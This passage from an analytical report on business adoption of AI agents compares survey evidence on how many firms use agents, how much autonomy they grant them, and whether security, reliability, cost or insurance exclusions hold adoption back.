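| Germany | 2026 | 37% of firms with 10 or more employees | 73% (250 or more) |

The countries' figures aren't strictly comparable, because the US survey covers the past two weeks and the Canadian one covers the past year. US use was still rising slowly, to just over 21% in the second quarter, according to TechInformed. Most use is also shallow, with only 10% of the UK firms that use AI saying they use it extensively.

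Surveys of executives produce much higher numbers. *Monitoring AI Adoption in the US Economy* (Allen, 2026) compares two US surveys from late 2025, which found adoption rates of 18% and 78%. The lower figure is the share of firms that use AI, and the higher one is roughly the share of workers whose employer uses it. Suppose 99 firms employ ten people each and one employs 1,000. If only the largest firm uses AI, 1% of firms use it, but about half of all workers have an employer that does.

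Allen thinks differences like this are probably the main reason for the gap. They can't be the whole reason, because *The Microstructure of AI Diffusion* (2026) weights the Census Bureau's own survey by employment and gets only 32%. Executives may know about more of their firm's projects than other respondents do, or may feel pressure to say there are some.

Far fewer firms had agents when DSIT asked in 2025. Of the 16% of UK businesses that used AI, 7% used agents, including pilots, which is about 1% of all businesses. In follow-up interviews, few people knew what "agentic AI" meant.

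Business surveys give higher figures for agents and help distinguish firms that have tried an agent from those that use one in production and those that let one act without approval. Lichtenberg (2025), in *HBR*, describes a survey by Harvard Business Review Analytic Services. Security Management's *From Data Theft to Security Control Doubts* covers one by the Ponemon Institute, and Cybersecurity Dive covers one by the consulting firm KPMG. Docker, which makes software for packaging and isolating programs, ran its own survey.

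| Survey | Trying agents | Using agents | Letting agents act alone |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harvard Business Review | 50% piloting or exploring | 9% fully deployed | 6% fully trust agents to run core processes |
| Ponemon | Not reported | 15% fully adopted, 23% partly | Not reported |
| KPMG | 30% testing | More than half deploying | 43% forbid it in certain high-risk uses |
| Docker | Not reported | 60% in production, a third of them at an early stage | Not reported |

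Many of these firms have tried an agent and a growing number use one, but few trust one to run important processes alone. The 6% figure measures trust rather than practice, since a firm can trust an agent and still have someone check its work. In the same survey, 43% trusted agents only with limited or routine tasks, and 39% only with supervised or non-core ones. KPMG found that nearly 60% of businesses planned to have employees validate every output.

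The sample makes a large difference here too. *Canadian firms slow to employ AI agents, survey shows* (Hemmadi, 2026) reports that 44% of executives at large and growing Canadian business-software companies said their companies had adopted agents, while only 19% of all Canadian businesses used AI of any kind. Definitions vary as well. In October, Alexander and Xiao advised readers of *An agentic bank?* (2026) to doubt banks' claims of AI adoption, because banks have no clear definition of it and no way to measure the return.

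### Who asks and who answers

Security is the top reason for holding back in several of these surveys. *Security chiefs hit brakes on risky agentic AI roll-out* (Mitchell, 2026) describes a survey by Apono with the same result. The table shows who paid for each survey and who answered it.

| Survey | Sponsor | Respondents | Date | Finding on security |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Harvard Business Review | Workato (automation software) and Amazon Web Services | 603 business and technology leaders | July 2025 | 31% name cybersecurity and privacy as a main challenge |
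| Apono | Apono (access controls) | 250 senior security professionals | December 2025 | 98% say security and data concerns have affected agent projects |
| Ponemon | OpenText (business and security software) | 1,878 IT and IT security staff | Published March 2026 | 43% lack proper risk and security controls |
| KPMG | KPMG (consulting) | Senior leaders at large companies | 2026 | 75% worry about the cybersecurity and privacy risks of AI |
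| Docker | Docker (tools for isolating software) | More than 800 developers and decision makers | Early 2026 | 40% call security the top blocker in building agents |

All the sponsors sell something that a worried firm might buy. This gives them a reason to ask about security and publicise the answer, but it doesn't make the worry false.

Apono's 98% includes every respondent whose organisation had slowed a project, narrowed it or added a review step over security, so it doesn't mean that security stopped nearly every project. Of all respondents, 77% reported moderate slowdowns or extra scrutiny, and 21% reported significant delays or reduced scope. Reviewing risky projects is part of a security team's job, so a low figure would arguably have been more alarming. The 98% also doesn't measure whether security mattered more than cost or reliability.

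People in different jobs answer the same question differently. When Ponemon asked whether organisations had tools or processes to respond to misuse involving data leaks and prompt injection, 65% of top executives said yes, compared with 35% of staff and technicians.

The list of possible answers matters too. Ponemon's respondents gave these reasons for not adopting agents:

| Reason | Share of respondents |
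|---|---|
| Lack of proper risk and security controls | 43% |
| Complex system integration | 38% |
| Data quality | 33% |
| Cost | 32% |
| Unclear business value | 28% |
| Lack of in-house expertise | 26% |

Security is the most common answer in Ponemon's survey, but the other obstacles are split across five answers. Integration, data quality and expertise are all part of getting an agent to work. If Ponemon had combined them into one answer, at least 38% would have chosen it, and the total could easily have passed security's 43%. Harvard Business Review's list also puts security first, at 31%, followed by separate answers for output quality (23%), unready business processes (22%) and infrastructure (22%).

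The most common answer in Ponemon's survey also describes something the firm lacks but could buy or build. A respondent could choose that answer without believing that an agent's attack surface is unbounded.

### What official surveys found about security

Statistics offices don't sell security products, but the answer options they offer also affect their survey results. DSIT's main list of barriers included skills, cost, ethics and unclear regulation, but not security. In DSIT's follow-up interviews, where businesses could answer in their own words, data security and accurate output were the most common difficulties in deploying AI safely. Most businesses said their concerns about trust had not prevented or delayed deployment. DSIT's list therefore left out a common concern, but the interviews don't suggest that it was usually decisive.

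Statistics Canada did offer cybersecurity or privacy as an answer, and it came first. Only 13.4% of businesses chose it, just ahead of cost at 10.6%, but the share rises steeply with size:

| Employees | Cybersecurity or privacy limits AI use | AI is not relevant to the business |
|---|---|---|
| 1 to 4 | 11.6% | 41.4% |
| 20 to 99 | 22.3% | 34.3% |
| 100 or more | 30.0% | 21.3% |

This is better evidence for the security explanation than any of the sponsored surveys. Larger businesses are more likely to see a use for AI, and also more likely to say that security or privacy limits it. But the question covers all AI, so some respondents may have been thinking of staff who paste customer records into a chatbot. And 70% of the larger businesses didn't choose that answer.

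Percentages also depend on which firms a survey counts. In Eurostat's 2025 data, concerns about data protection kept 53% of the firms that had considered AI from using it. Euronews (2026) reports the same concern as a share of all firms, about 8%. Privacy can therefore look like a major or a minor obstacle, depending on which figure is cited.

### What teams do in production

People who build agents can describe the difficulties more precisely than executives can in a questionnaire. *Measuring Agents in Production* (Pan, Arabzadeh et al., 2025) reports a survey of 306 practitioners and interviews with 20 teams, conducted between April and November 2025. Its main survey results cover 86 agents in production or pilots, though not every respondent answered every question.

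Most of these agents worked within tight limits. In the survey, 68% ran for at most ten steps before a person had to intervene, and 47% for fewer than five. Of the 20 teams interviewed, 16 had fixed the general sequence of tasks in advance. People checked the output of 74% of the agents, sometimes alongside automated methods.

Reliability was the main difficulty. Technical performance, which includes reliability, was the top priority for 38% of practitioners, compared with 17% for compliance and 3% for governance. The teams interviewed said they put quality and correctness ahead of security. They weren't very concerned about running costs, because the agents saved the time of doctors, engineers and other expensive staff.

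This strongly supports the fourth view, but the sample favours it. The 86 projects couldn't include any that a security team had stopped before the pilot. The researchers also recruited many respondents through their own networks and events for people who build agents. Some of the obstacles they recorded were partly about security. Five of the 20 teams had trouble connecting agents to older systems under existing security and compliance rules, which limited what the agents could do or where the teams could use them.

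Alvanakis Apostolou, Bosch and Holmström Olsson (2026), in *Agentic AI in Industry*, did look at work that hadn't reached production. They interviewed 16 practitioners at 12 companies about AI in software development. In production, seven companies used only assistants, four gave agents limited tasks such as reviewing code, and one ran several agents together. Four companies had also experimented with more capable systems that weren't yet part of their normal work.

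The interviews revealed four recurring barriers:

- **Scattered information:** the agent couldn't find or take in everything it needed from the company's code, documents and requirements.
- **Unfamiliar material:** models did badly with programming languages, tools and terms that only the company used.
- **Unpredictable behaviour:** nobody could define the agent's limits well enough to approve it for some jobs.
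- **Confidentiality:** some data couldn't leave the company's premises.

Prompt injection isn't on the list, but another security concern, confidentiality, made some companies' agents less reliable. These companies had to run smaller local models, which were less capable than cloud models. If one of them cited poor performance as an obstacle, its own security rules would be part of the cause.

One company subject to safety rules built a system of agents that assessed the risks of malfunctions and drafted a table of requirements, but couldn't use it for safety work because that required documentation of how the tool might behave. Alvanakis Apostolou and colleagues call this a verification gap, meaning that the agent may be capable but the company has no scalable way to show that its output is acceptable. Their sample is small and covers only software development, where tests can catch some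 errors automatically. A decision about a customer's claim could be harder to check.

### Mistakes or attacks?

Human review and limits on the number of steps an agent can take could protect a firm from the agent's mistakes, from attackers or from both. Asking what each control would stop is one way to tell which of these the firm is worried about.

A limit on steps mainly helps with mistakes. If an agent gets each step right 98% of the time and its errors are independent, it completes ten steps without an error 82% of the time (0.98^10), but fifty steps only 36% of the time. A person who checks after ten steps can stop the errors from piling up. The limit helps less against fraud, which may need only one step. Redirecting the Brook Cleaning payment, for example, takes a single tool call.

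The teams Pan and colleagues interviewed gave similar reasons for limiting their agents' autonomy: hard problems, unpredictable planning and slow responses. *The Hierarchy of Agentic Capabilities* (2026) also suggests that firms limit autonomy because models aren't yet reliable enough to work alone for long. Models have improved at long tasks since those interviews, so firms may have loosened some of these limits.

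Random checks are also better at catching mistakes than attacks. Two of the 20 teams had a second model score each answer, sent the doubtful ones to experts and checked a random sample of the rest. That is a sensible way to estimate an error rate. But a fraudster may send only one invoice, which a random sample could miss, and can word it so that the resulting answer scores well.

Other controls limit the damage an agent can do, whether it makes a mistake or follows an attacker's instructions. For example, an agent may be able to write a bug report but not change the software. The teams treated security largely as a by-product of restrictions like this one. Several teams also gave agents to their own employees first, to reduce both kinds of risk.

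The evidence therefore suggests that builders limit their agents mainly because of reliability. More reliable models would not necessarily remove the need for limits, because either mistakes or attacks are enough of a reason to keep people involved. If a new model never misread an honest invoice, the insurer could drop its random checks, but it would still want a person to confirm a changed account number in case an attacker had sent it. The insurer would still need the random checks if the model never fell for a hostile email but misread one invoice in 200. As models make fewer mistakes, security should account for more of the remaining hesitation.

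The effects of security measures can also look like a poor return. Suppose the agent saves five minutes on each of the insurer's 1,000 weekly invoices, or about 83 hours a week. If a security rule requires a person to spend three minutes approving each payment, the saving falls to about 33 hours. The insurer might then report in a survey that the agent has unclear business value, although the rule removed most of the benefit. In a KPMG survey, 58% of respondents said that cybersecurity risks made it difficult to demonstrate a return on AI.

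### Banks and hospitals

Banks and insurers face strict security and regulatory demands, yet they are among the fastest to adopt AI, so these concerns do not keep firms away from it altogether. In May, 34% of US finance and insurance firms used AI, compared with 20% of all firms, and in Canada the figures were 40% and 19%. Of the deployed agents that Pan and colleagues surveyed, 44% were used in finance or banking. None of these figures measures how much agents are allowed to do on their own.

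The best-documented examples have narrow tasks. One team that Pan and colleagues interviewed runs an agent that prepares clinicians' requests for insurance approval of treatment. It always checks the patient's coverage first, then whether the treatment is medically necessary, then the risks. A contract stops the model's supplier from training on the medical records. The agent's accuracy is hard to measure because mistakes may come to light only when somebody loses money or a patient's approval is late. The consumer lender described earlier, whose agents check applicants' identities, sends about one case in five to a person.

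Some large institutions have announced that they use agents. BNY, a US bank, said in 2025 that dozens of its "digital employees" had their own logins and worked under human managers on jobs such as fixing flaws in code and checking payment instructions. The same year, Universal Health Services, a US hospital operator, began using agents from Hippocratic AI to phone patients after they went home. Banks and hospitals don't have to publish a full list of their agents, so these announcements can't show how many others are in use or how many projects failed.

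Security is a clearer obstacle when the agent belongs to a customer. At a June conference, experts warned that banks had not designed their fraud and identity controls for software acting as the customer (Pape, 2026, *Banks aren't ready for AI agents moving money, experts warn*). Several large US banks restricted such agents that autumn, although they also had a commercial interest in keeping deposits.

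In healthcare, privacy and regulation seem to matter more than in most industries. Statistics Canada found that 26% of businesses in healthcare and social assistance said cybersecurity or privacy limited their use of AI, and 18% said the same of regulation. Regulation worries some British financial firms too. Of the finance and real estate businesses that told DSIT unclear rules had kept them from adopting AI, 81% called the lack of clarity a significant barrier.

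### Insurance that leaves out AI

Some insurers have begun to exclude AI from their policies, so firms may not be able to insure against the losses they can't prevent. Since January 2026, US insurers have been able to add standard exclusions for generative AI to general liability policies, using wording from Verisk, a company that drafts policy forms for the industry. W. R. Berkley, a US insurer, has drafted a broader exclusion for some management and professional liability policies, which applies to claims arising from almost any use of AI.

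The effect depends on the kind of loss. General liability insurance pays when a firm injures someone, damages their property or, for example, defames them. An exclusion from that coverage would matter to a hospital whose agent gave a patient dangerous advice. It would make no difference to a firm whose agent paid a thief, because general liability insurance doesn't cover the firm's own stolen money.

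A crime policy might cover the stolen money, since some pay when a fraudster tricks an employee into sending a payment. If the policy mentions only employees, the firm may have to argue that tricking its agent also counts, and it may not get an answer until after a loss. The firm would be wise to ask the insurer to settle the wording before the agent goes live.

Some insurers instead see an opportunity in covering AI risks. In 2025 Armilla began offering policies, backed by underwriters at Lloyd's of London, that cover losses when an AI system performs worse than expected. Such a policy could replace an uncertain loss with a known annual cost, though the insurer would probably want evidence of the system's performance before setting a price.

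It isn't clear how many firms have delayed adopting agents because of insurance exclusions. Neither DSIT's list of barriers nor the reasons reported from Ponemon's survey include insurance, so a firm that held back for lack of cover might have cited cost or risk controls instead.

### Employees who don't wait

A firm that delays may find that its staff already use AI. In mid-2026, 55% of British workers told the ONS that they used AI for work or education, while 35% of UK businesses with ten or more employees reported using it. The gap does not show how many people are breaking their employer's rules, because the first figure includes self-employed people and study outside work, and large employers can raise it, as in the US surveys. However, *The Microstructure of AI Diffusion* confirms that workers sometimes use AI when their firm has not formally adopted it.

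Unapproved use of AI has its own risks. Suppose the insurer bans AI from its accounts department, and a clerk pastes supplier emails into a personal chatbot account to summarise them. The insurer has no contract with the chatbot's provider and no log of what the clerk shared. If the clerk instead connects a personal agent to the work mailbox, hostile emails can reach an agent that the insurer doesn't know about and can't shut off.

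This weakens the case for waiting, because some risk remains even if the insurer approves no agents. But it doesn't justify giving an agent access to payments, because a clerk who wants help with emails doesn't need an agent that can pay suppliers. The insurer could offer an approved assistant that reads and summarises invoices but can't send messages or money, and block unapproved tools from connecting to the mailbox. Staff would then have less reason to use their own tools, and the insurer could take its time deciding whether to let an agent make payments.
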